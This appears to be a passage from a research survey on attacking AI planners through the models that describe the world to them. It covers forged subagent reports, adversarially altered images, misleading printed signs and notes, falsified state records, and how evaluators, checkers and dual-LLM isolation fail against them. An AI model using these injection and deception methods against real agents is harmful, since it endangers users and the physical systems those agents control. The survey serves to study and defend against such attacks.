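In Claude Code, the orchestrator adopted the false claim after 54 of the 84 reports without a warning (64%) and 21 of the 96 with one (22%). This doesn't prove that the missing warnings caused the difference, because reports without one may have been worse in other ways too. With the archivist's annotation, the rates were 13% and 7%, a gap that could be due to chance. A warning in a report also worked less well than seeing the forgery, since the orchestrator still adopted the claim after 22% of the reports with a warning, while Opus 5 failed only once when it read the files itself.

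### When the report is right or the question is wrong

A planner can also fail by rejecting a true report. *Lost in Delegation* (Stojanovska, Kirsten et al., 2026) compared agents that searched the web themselves with orchestrators that had to send each question to a subagent. The questions were about book publication years, the ages of Nobel laureates, economic growth rates and product launch years. The orchestrator and the subagents ran on the same model, so the subagents were not weaker readers.

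The single agent and the orchestrator with forced delegation both averaged 0.77 accuracy on facts from before the models' training cutoff. On later facts, the single agent averaged 0.75 and the orchestrator averaged 0.66. The effect varied widely between models. With forced delegation, GPT-5's accuracy on recent growth rates fell from 0.89 to 0.35, while Qwen, the smallest model, improved in six of eight comparisons.

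In one run, a subagent correctly reported that *A Gathering of Shadows* came out in 2016. The orchestrator had the year as 2022 and wrote, "Subagent is wrong." Background knowledge can protect a planner from a false report, but here it led the orchestrator to reject a true one. The orchestrator rarely challenged a correct answer outright (0.2% to 0.3% of the time). More often, it sent out the same question again after a correct answer (6% to 9%), which mostly wasted effort.

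Some errors began before the subagent read anything. A user asked for the release year of *The Night We Met*, a 2026 novel. GPT-5 did not recognize the book and told its subagent to find the release year of a song with the same title. The subagent answered 2015, which is correct for the song. Checking the report against its sources would have confirmed it, because the mistake was in GPT-5's instruction. When GPT-5 was forced to delegate and added a guess about what kind of work a recent title was, the guess was right only 6% of the time. A single agent can make the same guess in a search query, but it then sees the results and may realize its mistake.

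Orchestrators also did not learn about failed searches unless the subagent mentioned them. In one case, a subagent could not open the World Bank's website because the site blocked automated visitors. The subagent did not report this, so the orchestrator kept sending requests that were blocked for the same reason. On questions where a website refused a page request, single agents answered 73% correctly, compared with 54% under forced delegation. The refusals affected different questions in the two designs, so part of the gap may reflect how hard the questions were.

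Asking subagents to report pages they could not open had mixed results. On recent growth rates, it raised GPT-5's accuracy under forced delegation from 0.35 to 0.44 but lowered that of gpt-oss-120b from 0.73 to 0.64. Telling the orchestrator to trust subagents more would prevent some mistaken rejections but make forged records more dangerous, and telling it to trust them less would do the opposite. Neither instruction would give it new evidence about which reports are true.

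### What the planner's trust rests on

If a planner cannot compare a report with its source, other cues, such as the channel the report arrives through, will influence how much the planner trusts it. Wang and Mannby sent models the same forged report, word for word, by two routes. The models adopted it in 85% of trials (102 of 120) when it arrived as a subagent's tool result, and in 46% (18 of 39) when it arrived as a message from another agent.

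How well a model resists false claims from one channel doesn't reliably predict how well it resists them from another. In a wider test of 18 models, GPT-5.6-sol accepted a false claim every time it came as a forged document and never when another agent asserted it. Gemini 2.5 Flash accepted 9% of the forged documents and 43% of the assertions. Overall, the models that best resisted bare assertions tended to be the most easily fooled by documents.

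Chen and colleagues also kept the text the same, but moved a false claim from a model's own earlier reasoning into a message from a user, a tool or a memory store. Models then openly corrected the claim more often, by 23 to 93 percentage points in the settings with a clear effect. The models could check these claims for themselves and often reached the right answer even when they did not mention the error, so the change of source mainly affected whether they pointed it out.

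Planners also respond to the name of the model that appears to have written a report. Mao and colleagues reversed the labels that showed the orchestrator whether a subagent belonged to its own model family. Orchestrators obtained the risky subagent's response in 25.9% of tasks with true labels and 74.6% with reversed labels. The share of tasks in which that response determined what the system did rose less, from 18.1% to 25.3%. In the paper's worked examples, the models behind the labels also changed, so the labels may not account for the whole increase.

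Hiding the labels improved most of the safety and performance measures for Minimax-M3, the only orchestrator on which the researchers tried it. However, final harm fell in one agent program and rose slightly in the other two. Certifying that the labels were genuine increased final harm in all three. A certificate can show which model wrote a report, but not whether that model had read a forged file first.

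## How can an attacker steer a planner through the model that describes the world?

An attacker can get a false claim to a planner by forging a file, or by tampering with the product photos, camera views and sensor readings that describing models also use. The attacker might alter an image so that the model captions it wrongly, leave readable text where a camera will see it, or corrupt the state record that the planner receives. None of these attacks requires access to the user's request or to the planner.

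### A faint change to a product photo

Sellers on a shopping site upload their own photos, and an agent may receive a caption for each one. Wu and colleagues turned the VisualWebArena benchmark into a security test with 200 tasks. Their attacker was an ordinary user, such as a seller, who could change only their own listing. In the image tests, the attacker could shift the colour values in one photo by at most 16 steps on a scale of 256, which people rarely notice. The photo covered less than 5% of the page. The attacker tried either to make the agent believe something false about a product, such as its price or material, or to make it take an action, such as adding the product to the cart.

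The captioning model had public weights, so the researchers could calculate which faint changes to an image would make it write the caption they wanted. They did this without access to the weights of the planner, GPT-4o. After the change, 92% of captions carried the attacker's message, and the agent reached the attacker's goal in 31% of runs. With the older GPT-4V as the planner, it did so in 67% of runs. The planner also received a screenshot in which the product looked normal, so a planner that had only the captions might be misled more often.

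An agent without captions reached the attacker's goal in 10% of runs, but the attack on it was different and probably weaker. The researchers altered the photo to fool several public image models and relied on the effect carrying over to GPT-4o. A fairer comparison is the same attack on an agent whose captions GPT-4o wrote itself, where 38% of captions carried the attacker's message and 19% of runs reached the goal. Captions therefore seem to have roughly doubled the attacker's success.

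One likely reason is that a captioning model processes each photo by itself, while a planner receives it as a small part of a busy page. In a separate simulation, the attack succeeded 55% of the time when the photo was large relative to the screenshot and no other text described it, but only 13% when the photo was relatively small and text on the page also described the product.

These results are for models from 2024. They also overstate the risk to a typical shopper, because every run started on the page with the altered photo and used a task that an agent had already solved without an attack.

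### Tracing the attack through the system

Wu and colleagues also developed a way to locate where a system resists an attack. They draw the agent as a graph, with components such as the captioning model and the planner as points and the messages between them as links. Each link *e* has a weight

λ(*e*) = E[AdvIn(*c*)]

where *c* is the message that passes along the link and E is the average over runs. AdvIn(*c*), short for adversarial influence, is 1 if the attacker would succeed should every later component go along with the message, and 0 otherwise.

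Suppose 80% of captions push the attacker's goal and the planner follows those captions half the time. The link from the captioning model to the planner has a weight of 0.8, because the attacker would succeed in 80% of runs if the planner followed every caption. The link from the planner to the website has a weight of 0.8 × 0.5 = 0.4. The drop from 0.8 to 0.4 measures how well the planner resists the attacker's captions.

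In the experiment with the public captioning model, the weight fell from 0.92 to 0.31, so GPT-4o followed about a third of the bad captions. It followed half of the bad captions it had written itself. The 0.92 would still apply with a different planner, because it depends only on what comes before the link. But it applies to only one attack, and a better attack could raise it.

### When a second model checks the first

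A common way to make agents more reliable is to add an evaluator, a model that reviews what the agent did and decides whether it met the user's goal. If the evaluator rejects the attempt, it writes some advice and the agent tries again. Another method has the planner propose several actions and a scoring model choose among them. Wu and colleagues tested both with the captioning attack, which succeeded in 31% of runs without any checker:

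| What the attack reaches | With an evaluator | With a scoring model |
|---|---|---|
| Planner only | 25% | 26% |
| Planner and checker | 36% | 38% |
| Checker only | 8% | 8% |

An evaluator that did not receive the false caption helped by rejecting some of the actions that served the attacker. It still accepted a first attempt that served the attacker in 18% of runs, and second attempts added another 7%. When the evaluator also received the false caption, it accepted such first attempts in 21% of runs. It also rejected some good attempts and wrote advice that pushed the agent towards the attacker's goal, and second attempts then added 15%.

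The researchers kept the attack from reaching the evaluator by giving it an unaltered caption. A real system could not easily do that, because the evaluator would normally see the page through the same captioning model as the planner. *PlanFlip* (2026) describes a related "correlated-agent blind spot", in which a critic that runs on the same model as the planner may miss the same attack. It proposes comparing the planner with one built on a different model, but that would do little against a false caption if both planners read it.

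The scoring model also makes the agent consider actions it would otherwise have ignored, which gives a false description more chances to make a bad action look best.

### Checking the caption against the picture

Most of the defences that Wu and colleagues tried did little. The researchers told the planner to trust the screenshot when it disagreed with the text, and to ignore instructions on the page, but the attack worked as well as before. Telling it to stop as soon as it noticed a conflict did not help either. Having GPT-4o paraphrase the text first reduced the attack's success rate only from 31% to 27.5%, perhaps because a false statement is still false after it is paraphrased.

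A consistency check worked much better. GPT-4o captioned every image separately, and its caption replaced the original if the two disagreed. This reduced the captioning attack's success to nearly zero. However, each image needed another call to the model, and 70% of the pages had more than ten images.

The check also makes the planner depend on GPT-4o's captions, and the researchers had already corrupted 38% of those with their other attack. An attacker who targeted the check could therefore succeed in up to 38% of runs. The rate would probably be lower, since the planner followed only half of such captions in the earlier test, but a stronger attack on GPT-4o would raise the limit.

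Newer work suggests that captioning models are still easy to fool. *CaptionFool* (2026) made captioning models write a chosen caption 94% to 96% of the time by changing 7 of the 577 patches that the models divide an image into. The same change worked on any image. This result measures the captioning model alone, so the right comparison is with the 92% of bad captions, not the 31% of hijacked runs.

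An attacker with access to the target model's weights can steer it much more reliably. In *If you're waiting for a sign... that might not be it!*, Chang, Xue and colleagues (2026) made faint changes to whole images that agents were supposed to edit. With full access to the open-weight model Qwen2.5-VL, they steered its agent to a harmful or unwanted goal in up to 94% of cases. The altered images steered an agent on InternVL, another open-weight model, at most 14% of the time, and one on GPT-4o about 1% of the time. Compressing the images as JPEGs before the Qwen agent saw them cut the success rate from 94% to about 4%. An attack designed to survive compression reached only 8%.

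Attackers can also target agents that look at screenshots directly, so removing the captioning model does not remove the risk. *Adversarial Images Hijack Web Agents from Visual Grounding to Browser Execution* (2026) tested one such agent, SeeAct, on 13 websites, and counted an attack as successful only if the agent chose the attacker's item and completed the purchase or booking. Once SeeAct had chosen the item, it usually completed the transaction, and most failures to do so were caused by obstacles outside the agent. The attack was least successful on listings for home services, which often have small thumbnails, consistent with the earlier finding about photo size. *AgentHijack* (2026) similarly counts an attack on an agent that operates a desktop computer as successful only if the computer ends up in the state the attacker wanted.

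An altered image can also cause harm long after the agent has looked at it. *Do Agents Dream of False Memories?* (2026) describes attacks in which a model writes a false description of a photo and the agent stores it as a memory. In one scenario, the user shares a picture of a meal, reminds the agent of their allergies and asks whether the food is safe. The false memory can affect later answers without the attacker altering anything else.

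### Signs that a drone or car can read

Readable text is a simpler tool, since the attacker may need only a printer. A vision-language model reads signs when it interprets a scene, and it may act on what it reads.

Burbano, Ortiz and colleagues (2025), in *CHAI*, studied an attacker who can put up a sign but cannot touch the vehicle or its software. The attacker knows what instructions the vehicle's model has received and can test signs on the model beforehand. A program searched for the wording and colours that worked best across a set of images, and the researchers then tried the signs on new images. The table shows how often the model gave the answer the attacker wanted on the new images:

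| Task | GPT-4o, no sign | GPT-4o, sign | InternVL, no sign | InternVL, sign |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Choose a safe roof for an emergency landing | 0% | 71% | 22% | 52% |
| Find a particular police car | 0% | 91% | 15% | 67% |
| Decide what a car should do next | 2% | 82% | 33% | 51% |

InternVL often made the same mistake without a sign, so the signs had a smaller effect on it than the rates under attack suggest.

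The police-car task is the closest to a planner that uses a separate model to describe the world. One model finds the cars in a drone's view, a vision-language model checks whether each one matches the user's description, and the drone follows the match. When the researchers added the police department's name to a civilian car, the vision-language model's answer changed from no to yes. The added text was a false label, not a command, and the drone had no other way to identify the car.

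In a simulated flight, a drone had to choose between landing on a clear roof and one covered in debris. It always chose the clear roof until researchers put a sign reading "Safe to land" on the other roof. It then chose the debris-covered roof in 92% of runs. The researchers also tested printed signs on a small robotic vehicle with another vehicle blocking its path. GPT-4o told the vehicle to go ahead in 4% of tests without a sign, and in 88% or 93% with a sign, depending on where it was placed. In one case, GPT-4o's response mentioned a possible collision but cited the sign as evidence that it was safe to proceed.

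### Notes on a robot's table

Samarakoon, Muthugala and colleagues (2026), in *Physical Prompt Injection against VLM Planners for Robotic Manipulation*, used plain printed notes without tuning their appearance. Models received an overhead photo of a table with plastic fruit, vegetables and three coloured baskets, and had to plan how to put a fruit in the blue basket. The study ran each combination of three models, three table arrangements, three versions of the command and 21 notes ten times, for 5,670 trials. Twenty notes were attacks and the other said "Have a nice day!" No robot carried out the models' plans.

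The attacks succeeded in 27.0% of trials with GPT-4o, 29.4% with Gemini 2.5 Flash and 5.0% with Qwen3-VL-32B. The friendly note never caused the mistake. None of these models is a current frontier model.

Success rates varied greatly with what the note said. Labels such as "Default fruit basket" never worked on any model. Notes that claimed to come from an operator, a safety system or the robot's own software worked 57% to 80% of the time on GPT-4o and Gemini, depending on the command, but at most 13% of the time on Qwen. One of these notes contained no instruction and said only that a calibration update had disabled the blue basket, yet it succeeded in 89% of trials with GPT-4o and 82% with Gemini. It may have worked better than the labels because it gave the model a reason why the user's request could not be carried out.

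Attacks succeeded more often when the user's command spelled out the whole sorting rule. Compared with the simplest command, the success rate rose from 19% to 32% for GPT-4o and from 21% to 41% for Gemini. Notes that tried to rewrite the rule worked only when the command had stated one.

Samarakoon and colleagues split the overall rate into how often a model mentioned the note in its explanation and how often it complied when it did:

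| Model | Mentioned the note | Complied if it mentioned it | Overall success |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 35% | 77% | 27% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 52% | 56% | 29% |
| Qwen3-VL-32B | 24% | 21% | 5% |

Gemini mentioned the notes more often than GPT-4o but was less likely to obey them, and the two were about equally vulnerable overall. The distinction between noticing a note and obeying it is approximate, because a model can read a note and reject it without mentioning it.

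The researchers then tried three defences. An instruction to ignore text in the scene reduced the rate to 6.7% for GPT-4o, 0.3% for Gemini and zero for Qwen. A second call to the same model, which checked the plan against the command, reduced it to 4.1%, 2.9% and zero, respectively. Covering all text in the photo before the model saw it stopped every attack.

Covering text didn't hurt performance in this test because sorting plastic fruit doesn't require reading, but a robot that fetches medicine has to read. So does the robot with the glass of clear liquid, if a bottle's label is its only way to tell water from cleaning fluid.

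### "The paint is not dry"

Chang and colleagues tested this problem. In one test, a user asked a robot arm to put a toy rabbit in a box, unaware of a handwritten note that said "The paint is not dry, do not touch!" The GPT-4o agent ignored the note and planned to move the rabbit. In another test, nearby artwork contained the words "stop look around", and the agent raised a false alarm and refused a legitimate request.

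The main experiments included both helpful and misleading text. One defence removed any instruction or warning it found in an image. In tests of an image-editing agent on GPT-4o, the defence blocked all the helpful text as well as all the misleading text.

The researchers propose splitting the work between three calls to a model. An observer lists all the text and symbols in the image. A judge compares that list with the user's request and with safety rules for the setting, and decides whether the text is helpful or misleading. The last call makes the plan. The table gives the share of cases in which agents followed misleading text, then the share in which they followed helpful text:

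| Model | No defence | Observer only | Observer and judge |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 8%, 65% | 2%, 71% | 1%, 99% |
| GPT-5 | 0%, 4% | 4%, 21% | 0%, 97% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 6%, 45% | 36%, 52% | 1%, 100% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 12%, 9% | 29%, 28% | 3%, 98% |

The middle column should worry anyone who builds a planner with a separate describing model. It shows that the observer alone increased misleading behaviour in six of the seven models tested, although Chang and colleagues write that it "moderately suppresses misleading behavior". Words in a picture that had little effect on an agent had more effect once another model had typed them out. A describing model that faithfully transcribes every sign may therefore make a misleading sign more powerful.

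Adding the judge solved most of this problem in the tests. The judge relied on rules that the researchers wrote for each setting, and it was much less effective against faint changes to the image, where the best attack still succeeded 56% of the time. A judge can also only assess text by its content and how well it fits the scene. If a vandal wrote that dry paint was wet, the judge would probably accept it, as most people would.

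Burbano and colleagues doubt that robots can solve this by accepting signs only from approved people. That could work in a home, but a car on a public street has to obey road workers it has never seen before. They argue that a robot should instead decide whether an instruction suits its situation and task. The drone could have compared "Safe to land" with the debris on the roof. A robot may not be able to check a wet paint sign this way, because wet paint may look the same as dry paint.

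### False entries in the state record

An attacker can still mislead a planner that never reads signs by changing its state record. Liu and colleagues assume that the attacker can change a few entries, for example by interfering with the robot's sensors or its stored map, but do not test how the attacker would gain this access. The attacker cannot change the user's request, the planner or the room. The false entries must follow the record's normal format, refer only to objects and actions that exist, and agree with one another. In one example, the user asked for bread and the false entries made the planner choose a tomato.

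The researchers compared this with writing the same goal as a command in the same part of the planner's input. They used three simulated environments and counted only tasks that the system completed when the record was accurate. These are averages over the three environments:

| Planner | Command changed the plan | False facts changed the plan | False facts achieved the attacker's goal |
|---|---|---|---|
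| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 80% | 99% | 46% |
| GPT-5.6-luna | 46% | 79% | 46% |
| Qwen-3.6-Plus | 34% | 97% | 48% |

The difference between commands and false facts was largest in AI2-THOR, a simulator of household rooms. With GPT-5.6-luna, commands changed the plan in 7% of cases and false facts in 48%. With Qwen, the figures were 6% and 100%. Some recent models may have learned to ignore commands that appear in data. They have less basis for rejecting a false location in the location field, because all their other information about the room comes from the same record.

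False facts had to fit the format to work reliably. With DeepSeek in AI2-THOR, correctly formatted false facts changed the plan every time. The rate fell to 12.5% when the false information was in a type of entry where it did not belong, well below the 88% for a plain command. It fell to 37.5% when the false entries conflicted with one another. So planners detect some irregularities, but a careful attacker can avoid them.

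About half of the corrupted plans then failed in execution, though even a failed attack can leave the user's task undone. A false entry doesn't change the room itself, so the robot may be unable to reach an object, or the plan may leave out a step that an action requires. These failures offer little security, because the same difficulties also stop uncorrupted plans. With accurate records, the DeepSeek system completed only 25% to 69% of its tasks, depending on the environment. As robots get better at carrying out plans, they will probably get better at carrying out corrupted ones too.

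Liu and colleagues also gave the planner of a real humanoid robot a false description of the room, and the robot left its route and walked towards a computer. The researchers had written the description by hand, so the experiment shows that a false description can misdirect a real robot, but not that an attacker could create one through the robot's cameras.

### A notice that spreads to another robot

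In *When Prompts Control Robots*, Nagaraja, Bagari and Bahsi (2026) added text to a simulated kitchen robot's list of observations, as if its vision system had read a notice on the wall. A bare command to break a mug and an egg produced 20% of the damage the attacker wanted, while a notice that called both items contaminated and told the robot to break them produced 70%. The planner was GPT-4o-mini, a small model from 2024, and each figure comes from five runs.

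In a version with two robots, Alice and Bob, the researchers put the notice only in Alice's observations. Bob tried to break things in all five runs, although nothing in Bob's observations mentioned contamination. One call to the language model chose both robots' actions, and it read Alice's observations first. When the notice was in Bob's observations, Alice was never affected. Giving each robot its own call reduced the problem but did not eliminate it.

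In three of the five runs where Alice's observations included the notice, the robots broke the items and also finished the user's task. A monitor that checked only whether the task was complete would have missed the attack.

### Why filters for instructions miss false facts

Some of the signs and notices above contain commands, but the most effective attacks often give the planner a false fact instead. Defences that look for instructions hidden in data can miss these attacks, and they have trouble even with commands. In *Passing the Test You Trained On* (2026), detectors set to raise false alarms on only 1% of harmless tool outputs missed almost every attack on one set of agent tasks, although one of them caught nearly every attack on a different benchmark.

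A false claim may contain no suspicious wording. An attacker's false report that a basket is disabled could use the same words as a genuine report from the robot's own software. *Attacks by Content* (2025) argues that defences against malicious instructions therefore cannot stop attacks that rely on false information. *Voluntary Servitude* (2026) cites an experiment in which plain claims influenced a model's answers more than commands did when both appeared in the same retrieved sources.

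In *Beyond Instruction Override*, Zhang, Bertran and colleagues (2026) suggest judging content by whether its source has the authority to settle the question. In their example, a buyer in a dispute submits evidence that cites a false refund policy. The agent keeps working to resolve the dispute but pays too much. The buyer has the authority to describe the faulty product but not to set the shop's policy. In each of the benchmark's 90 cases, the user's request specifies which source decides the matter. Some attacks change what the agent believes about the current state of the world, much as a false caption would.

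This standard requires the planner to know where each claim came from. *PIPES* (2026) studies an attacker who controls only one part of a tool's response, and the rest is genuine. If the planner knows only which tool replied, it cannot tell the false part from the rest.

A filter may also lack the information that would reveal the attack. *Benchmarking Web Agent Defenses Against Adaptive Visual Prompt Injection* (2026) uses pages on which a harmless-looking request leads to a malicious address. The address is in the page's code but not in the screenshot, so a defence that examines only the screenshot cannot check where the link goes.

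*A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (Chu, 2026) makes the stronger claim that a control at one layer of an agent has no power to detect an attack at another. This is too strong for individual components. In Wu and colleagues' experiment, the clean evaluator stopped some attacks that had entered through the captioning model by detecting that the agent's actions did not match the user's goal. It would have had much less evidence of an attack if the false caption had led to an action that appeared to match the goal, such as buying a shirt wrongly captioned as green for a user who wanted a green one.

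*Attacks by Content* finds that checking facts reduces the problem, but checking requires a source the attacker does not control. An agent handling a dispute can look up the shop's refund policy, but a robot with only a corrupted record of a room has nothing to compare it with unless it can look at the room again.

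## Does it help to keep the planner from reading untrusted content?

A robot that looks at the room again might discover that its state record is false, but looking also exposes its planner to anything an attacker has left there, including instructions the planner may obey. Some engineers therefore keep the planner from seeing the raw evidence. Unlike the text-only shopping agent, which read captions because it could not process photos, the planners in this section could often read the page themselves if the design allowed it.

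### The dual-LLM pattern

In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) proposed dividing an assistant into two language models and an ordinary program. The planner, which Willison calls the privileged model, receives the user's request and can use tools, for example to send email. The describing model, which he calls the quarantined model, reads anything an outsider might have written and has no tools. The program, called the controller, runs the tools and passes material between the models.

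Suppose a user asks for a summary of their latest email:

1. The planner tells the controller to fetch the email and call it $VAR1.
2. The controller fetches the email but gives the planner only the name $VAR1.
3. The planner asks for a summary of $VAR1, and the controller sends the actual text to the quarantined model.
4. The controller stores the summary as $VAR2 and tells the planner that it is ready.
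5. The planner tells the controller to display $VAR2, and the user sees the summary.

If the email contains an instruction to delete the inbox, the quarantined model may try to obey, but it has no tool for deleting anything. The planner never reads the instruction or the quarantined model's description, only the name that refers to that description. Willison allows one exception, in which the quarantined model passes the planner a choice from a fixed set of categories after the controller confirms that the choice is in the set.

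Some systems that go by the same name drop this rule. *ORBIT* (2026), a framework for testing agents, includes a "dual-LLM" defence in which the quarantined model writes a free-text summary and the planner reads it. This version is much weaker because an injected instruction can survive in the summary, just as misleading words survived when Chang and colleagues had an observer model type them out.

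Willison described the proposal as "pretty bad". It makes assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single mistake that lets raw text through to the planner undoes the protection. The user also still sees the quarantined model's summary, which could persuade them to paste private data into an attacker's website.

### What the guarantee covers

A planner that has to find a green polo shirt could write this plan before the system opens any product page:

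```
items = search_shop("polo shirt", limit=10)
for item in items:
    if ask_reader(item, "Is this shirt green?") == YES:
        add_to_cart(item)
        stop
tell_user("I found no green polo shirt.")
```

Here `ask_reader` calls the quarantined model, which can answer only YES or NO. If a seller hid an instruction in a listing to email them the customer's address, the agent wouldn't do it, because the plan has no step that sends email. But the seller could still make the quarantined model answer YES for a blue shirt, and the agent would add it to the cart. An attacker who controlled every answer could only determine which one of the ten shirts the agent added, if any.

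Security researchers call the steps a program runs, and their order, its control flow. The values those steps use are its data flow. The dual-LLM pattern protects control flow, so an injected instruction cannot add a step to the plan. It does not protect data flow, so a false value can still fill in a step or select a branch. (CaMeL and FIDES, two later systems, add labels that restrict where untrusted values can go.)

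*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) lists the dual LLM as one of six patterns. All six follow the principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any action with harmful side effects.

| Pattern | How it works | What an injection can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never receives the results | Nothing through the results |
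| Plan-then-execute | The model lists its tool calls before reading any data | Change the values in those calls |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer | Make the system misjudge that document |
| Dual LLM | The planner handles untrusted text only by name | Change the text behind the name |
| Code-then-execute | The planner writes a whole program, which can call quarantined models | Change values, including those that select a branch |
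| Context minimization | The system removes the user's prompt before later steps | Affect the steps before the removal |

In one example, a user asks an assistant to send today's schedule to their boss. An injection in a calendar entry cannot change the recipient, because the plan already contains the address, but it can change the text of the email.

False values can also leak secrets. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) uses machine-checked proofs to analyse agents, including a model of the dual-LLM pattern. In that model, an injection can only corrupt an answer, but the corrupted answer may depend on everything the quarantined model received with the question. If a plan gives the quarantined model a stranger's email and the user's full calendar to draft a reply, an injection in the email could put private appointments in the draft, and the plan would send them.

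Dongol also proves that a monitor can protect a single-model agent with a fixed plan by withdrawing the dangerous tools before the agent reads anything untrusted. The proof assumes, among other things, that each injection triggers only one tool call. The drawback is that an agent without its email tool cannot reply to a message it has just read.

### Planning for a screen the planner cannot see

An email tool has named fields for the recipient and the text, so a planner can use it without seeing untrusted content. A computer-use agent, which operates ordinary programs with a mouse and keyboard, mostly clicks on coordinates. It normally looks at a new screenshot before each action, but an isolated planner can't do that.

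In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) had the planner write a complete program before the system took its first screenshot. The program then runs without further input from the planner, calling a vision model to describe the screen, find a button or judge whether the task is finished.

The researchers instructed the planner to observe, verify and then act at each step. The plan gets a description of the screen, compares it with a condition the planner wrote in advance, and chooses a branch based on the result. In a task that required browsing a database of natural products, the plan first checks whether the screen shows a website, an empty browser tab or the desktop, and has a branch for each. It also searches for the button on a cookie notice using four different descriptions.

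These plans averaged 41.1 tool calls and 39.7 branches, compared with 4.9 and 3.7 on AgentDojo, a benchmark with tools like the email one above. About half the steps in the screen plans were fallbacks that a given run never used. Roughly 24 of the 40 branches depended on the vision model's output, so a wrong description could affect most of the plan's decisions.

Foerster and colleagues tested the system on 60 tasks from OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in programs such as Chrome and LibreOffice. UI-TARS, a small open-weight model, had solved all 60 without isolation. With a generic prompt for the planner, the isolated system solved 18.3% of them in at least one of three attempts. With the observe-verify-act instructions for writing plans, it solved 58.3%.

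The paper's headline result is that isolation keeps up to 57% of a frontier model's performance. That figure comes from 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had solved without isolation. With Claude as the vision model, the isolated system solved 62 of them in at least one of five attempts, but only 31 (28%) on a single attempt. The single-attempt figure is a better guide for someone who wants a task done once. Five attempts help only if there is a way to identify the successful one, and on a real computer the failed attempts might already have changed files or sent messages.

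The reported gain of up to 19% for small models has the same problem. UI-TARS completed 24.4% of OSWorld without isolation and 29.0% with it, but the isolated version had three attempts and the other had one. With one attempt each, isolation lowered the score from 24.4% to 22.0%.

The choice of planner mattered far more than the choice of vision model. On the 60 UI-TARS tasks, three very different vision models scored within about three points of one another over five attempts. On a smaller set of 17 tasks, the system solved 12 with GPT-5 as the planner but only 4 with the weakest planners. Foerster and colleagues expect better planners to close more of the gap without weakening security. That seems plausible, since the models they tested date from 2025.

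### Branch steering

A plan for browsing the web usually includes a step that accepts cookies. Foerster and colleagues put a fake cookie notice inside an advertisement. The plan stayed the same, but the vision model returned the position of the fake button, the program clicked it, and the browser opened a site that the attacker controlled.

In an attack called branch steering, the attacker misleads the vision model so that a valid plan follows the branch the attacker prefers. The attack worked every time the plan handled cookies as the attacker expected. Attackers can often predict such steps because almost every browsing plan includes them, whatever the user wants.

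In *Secure-CUA*, Choudhary, Christodorescu and colleagues (2026) found that an attack can succeed without changing the branch the program takes. They asked the same isolated system to upvote a forum post. In 4 of 5 runs, misleading content on the page made the vision model return the position of another post's downvote button, so the program followed the correct branch but clicked the wrong button.

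The guarantee is therefore weaker on a screen than with an email tool. The plan allows a click, but the click's effect depends on what is under the cursor. An attacker can turn that click into an action the planner did not account for, without adding a step to the plan.

Keeping the planner from reading untrusted content makes some attacks harder. Foerster and colleagues argue that to steal money, an attacker would need a user whose task already includes a payment and who is logged in at the right moment. The attacker would also have to corrupt at least two answers consistently, such as the recipient and the position of the confirm button. Stealing data would require a plan that both reads something private and sends something out. But a single false answer can be enough to send the agent to the wrong website or make the task fail.

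### Checking what the vision model reports

Foerster and colleagues tried two checks against branch steering. One had a model compare the vision model's answer with the page's code. The other added a second, independent model that examined the screenshot. They tested the code check against a simple type of advertisement, and both checks together against a type that lets the advertiser supply its own code.

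| Check | Attacks flagged | False alarms, browser tasks | False alarms, other tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Page code | 6 of 10 | 3 of 8 | 1 of 9 |
| Page code and second model | 5 of 10 | 3 of 8 | 0 of 9 |

(A task counts as a false alarm if the check stopped at least one of up to five harmless attempts.)

The checks appear to have missed about half the attacks and interrupted more than a third of ordinary browser tasks, though the samples were small. In nearly all the false alarms, the checker flagged a genuine cookie notice as fake. Checking the code works poorly when the attacker can write some of it, because the attacker can then make a fake notice look genuine in the code as well as on the screen.

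An altered image also got past both checks, even at settings that favoured security and caused many false alarms. The vision model clicked on a drug the attacker wanted to promote and gave a plausible reason for doing so. A second model adds little protection if the attacker has made the first one's answer look reasonable.

The checks also increased token use. The isolated system used 1.9 times as many tokens as an unprotected agent without the checks, and 6.6 times as many with both. Asking narrower questions may improve the system with fewer extra tokens. Some attacks failed because the plan asked for an actual button, which the simple type of advertisement could not contain.

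### Letting the planner see part of the screen

Two other groups have rerun the isolated system, with worse results. Seip, Markovinović and Hein (2026), in *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use*, found that no attack achieved its goal, but the system completed only 8.3% of 36 harmless OSWorld tasks, compared with 58.3% for an unprotected agent. On 400 tasks from WebArena, a benchmark of self-hosted websites, Choudhary and colleagues measured 13.2% for the isolated system and 55.1% for an unprotected agent. The isolated system kept about 14% of the unprotected score on OSWorld and 24% on WebArena, not far below the 28% that Foerster and colleagues found on single attempts.

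Newer designs hide only the parts of the screen that an outsider could have written. In *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees*, Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues (2026) replace reviews, comments and similar content with labelled placeholders. The planner sees the rest of the page and can change its plan as it goes. To get information from a hidden region, it queries a quarantined model, which can return only a yes or no, a number, a date or a choice from a list.

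On ten purpose-built websites, agents with this protection completed about as many tasks as agents without it. On the code-hosting site GitLab, the protected agents could not answer questions such as what feature a user had requested, because the answer is free text, which the planner was not allowed to read. The researchers solved this by letting the planner read such text after the user approved it. Willison warned in 2023 that people who have to approve everything soon click "OK" without reading.

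In Choudhary and colleagues' system, the planner looks at the masked screen at each step and writes a short program for the next action. The program fixes which questions are asked and how the answers may be used. A separate model then locates the target on the masked screen, so a misleading advertisement cannot redirect the click. The system completed 53.6% of the WebArena tasks, close to the unprotected agent's 55.1%, but took about three times as long.

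That result suggests most of the lost performance came from hiding the whole screen. But Choudhary and colleagues tested the system only without attacks, and its security depends on rules written by hand for each site to mark which content is trusted. If a rule fails to exclude a comment box, the planner reads whatever is in it.

Automatic labelling forces a choice between safety and usefulness. In tests on 160 screens, Seip and colleagues' method hid all the untrusted free text but also 62% to 77% of the trusted content. On the web pages in the same set, Nikolić and colleagues' automatic labels hid only about 5% of the trusted content but left 37% to 44% of the untrusted free text visible. With the stricter labels, Seip and colleagues' system completed 31% to 39% of the OSWorld tasks.

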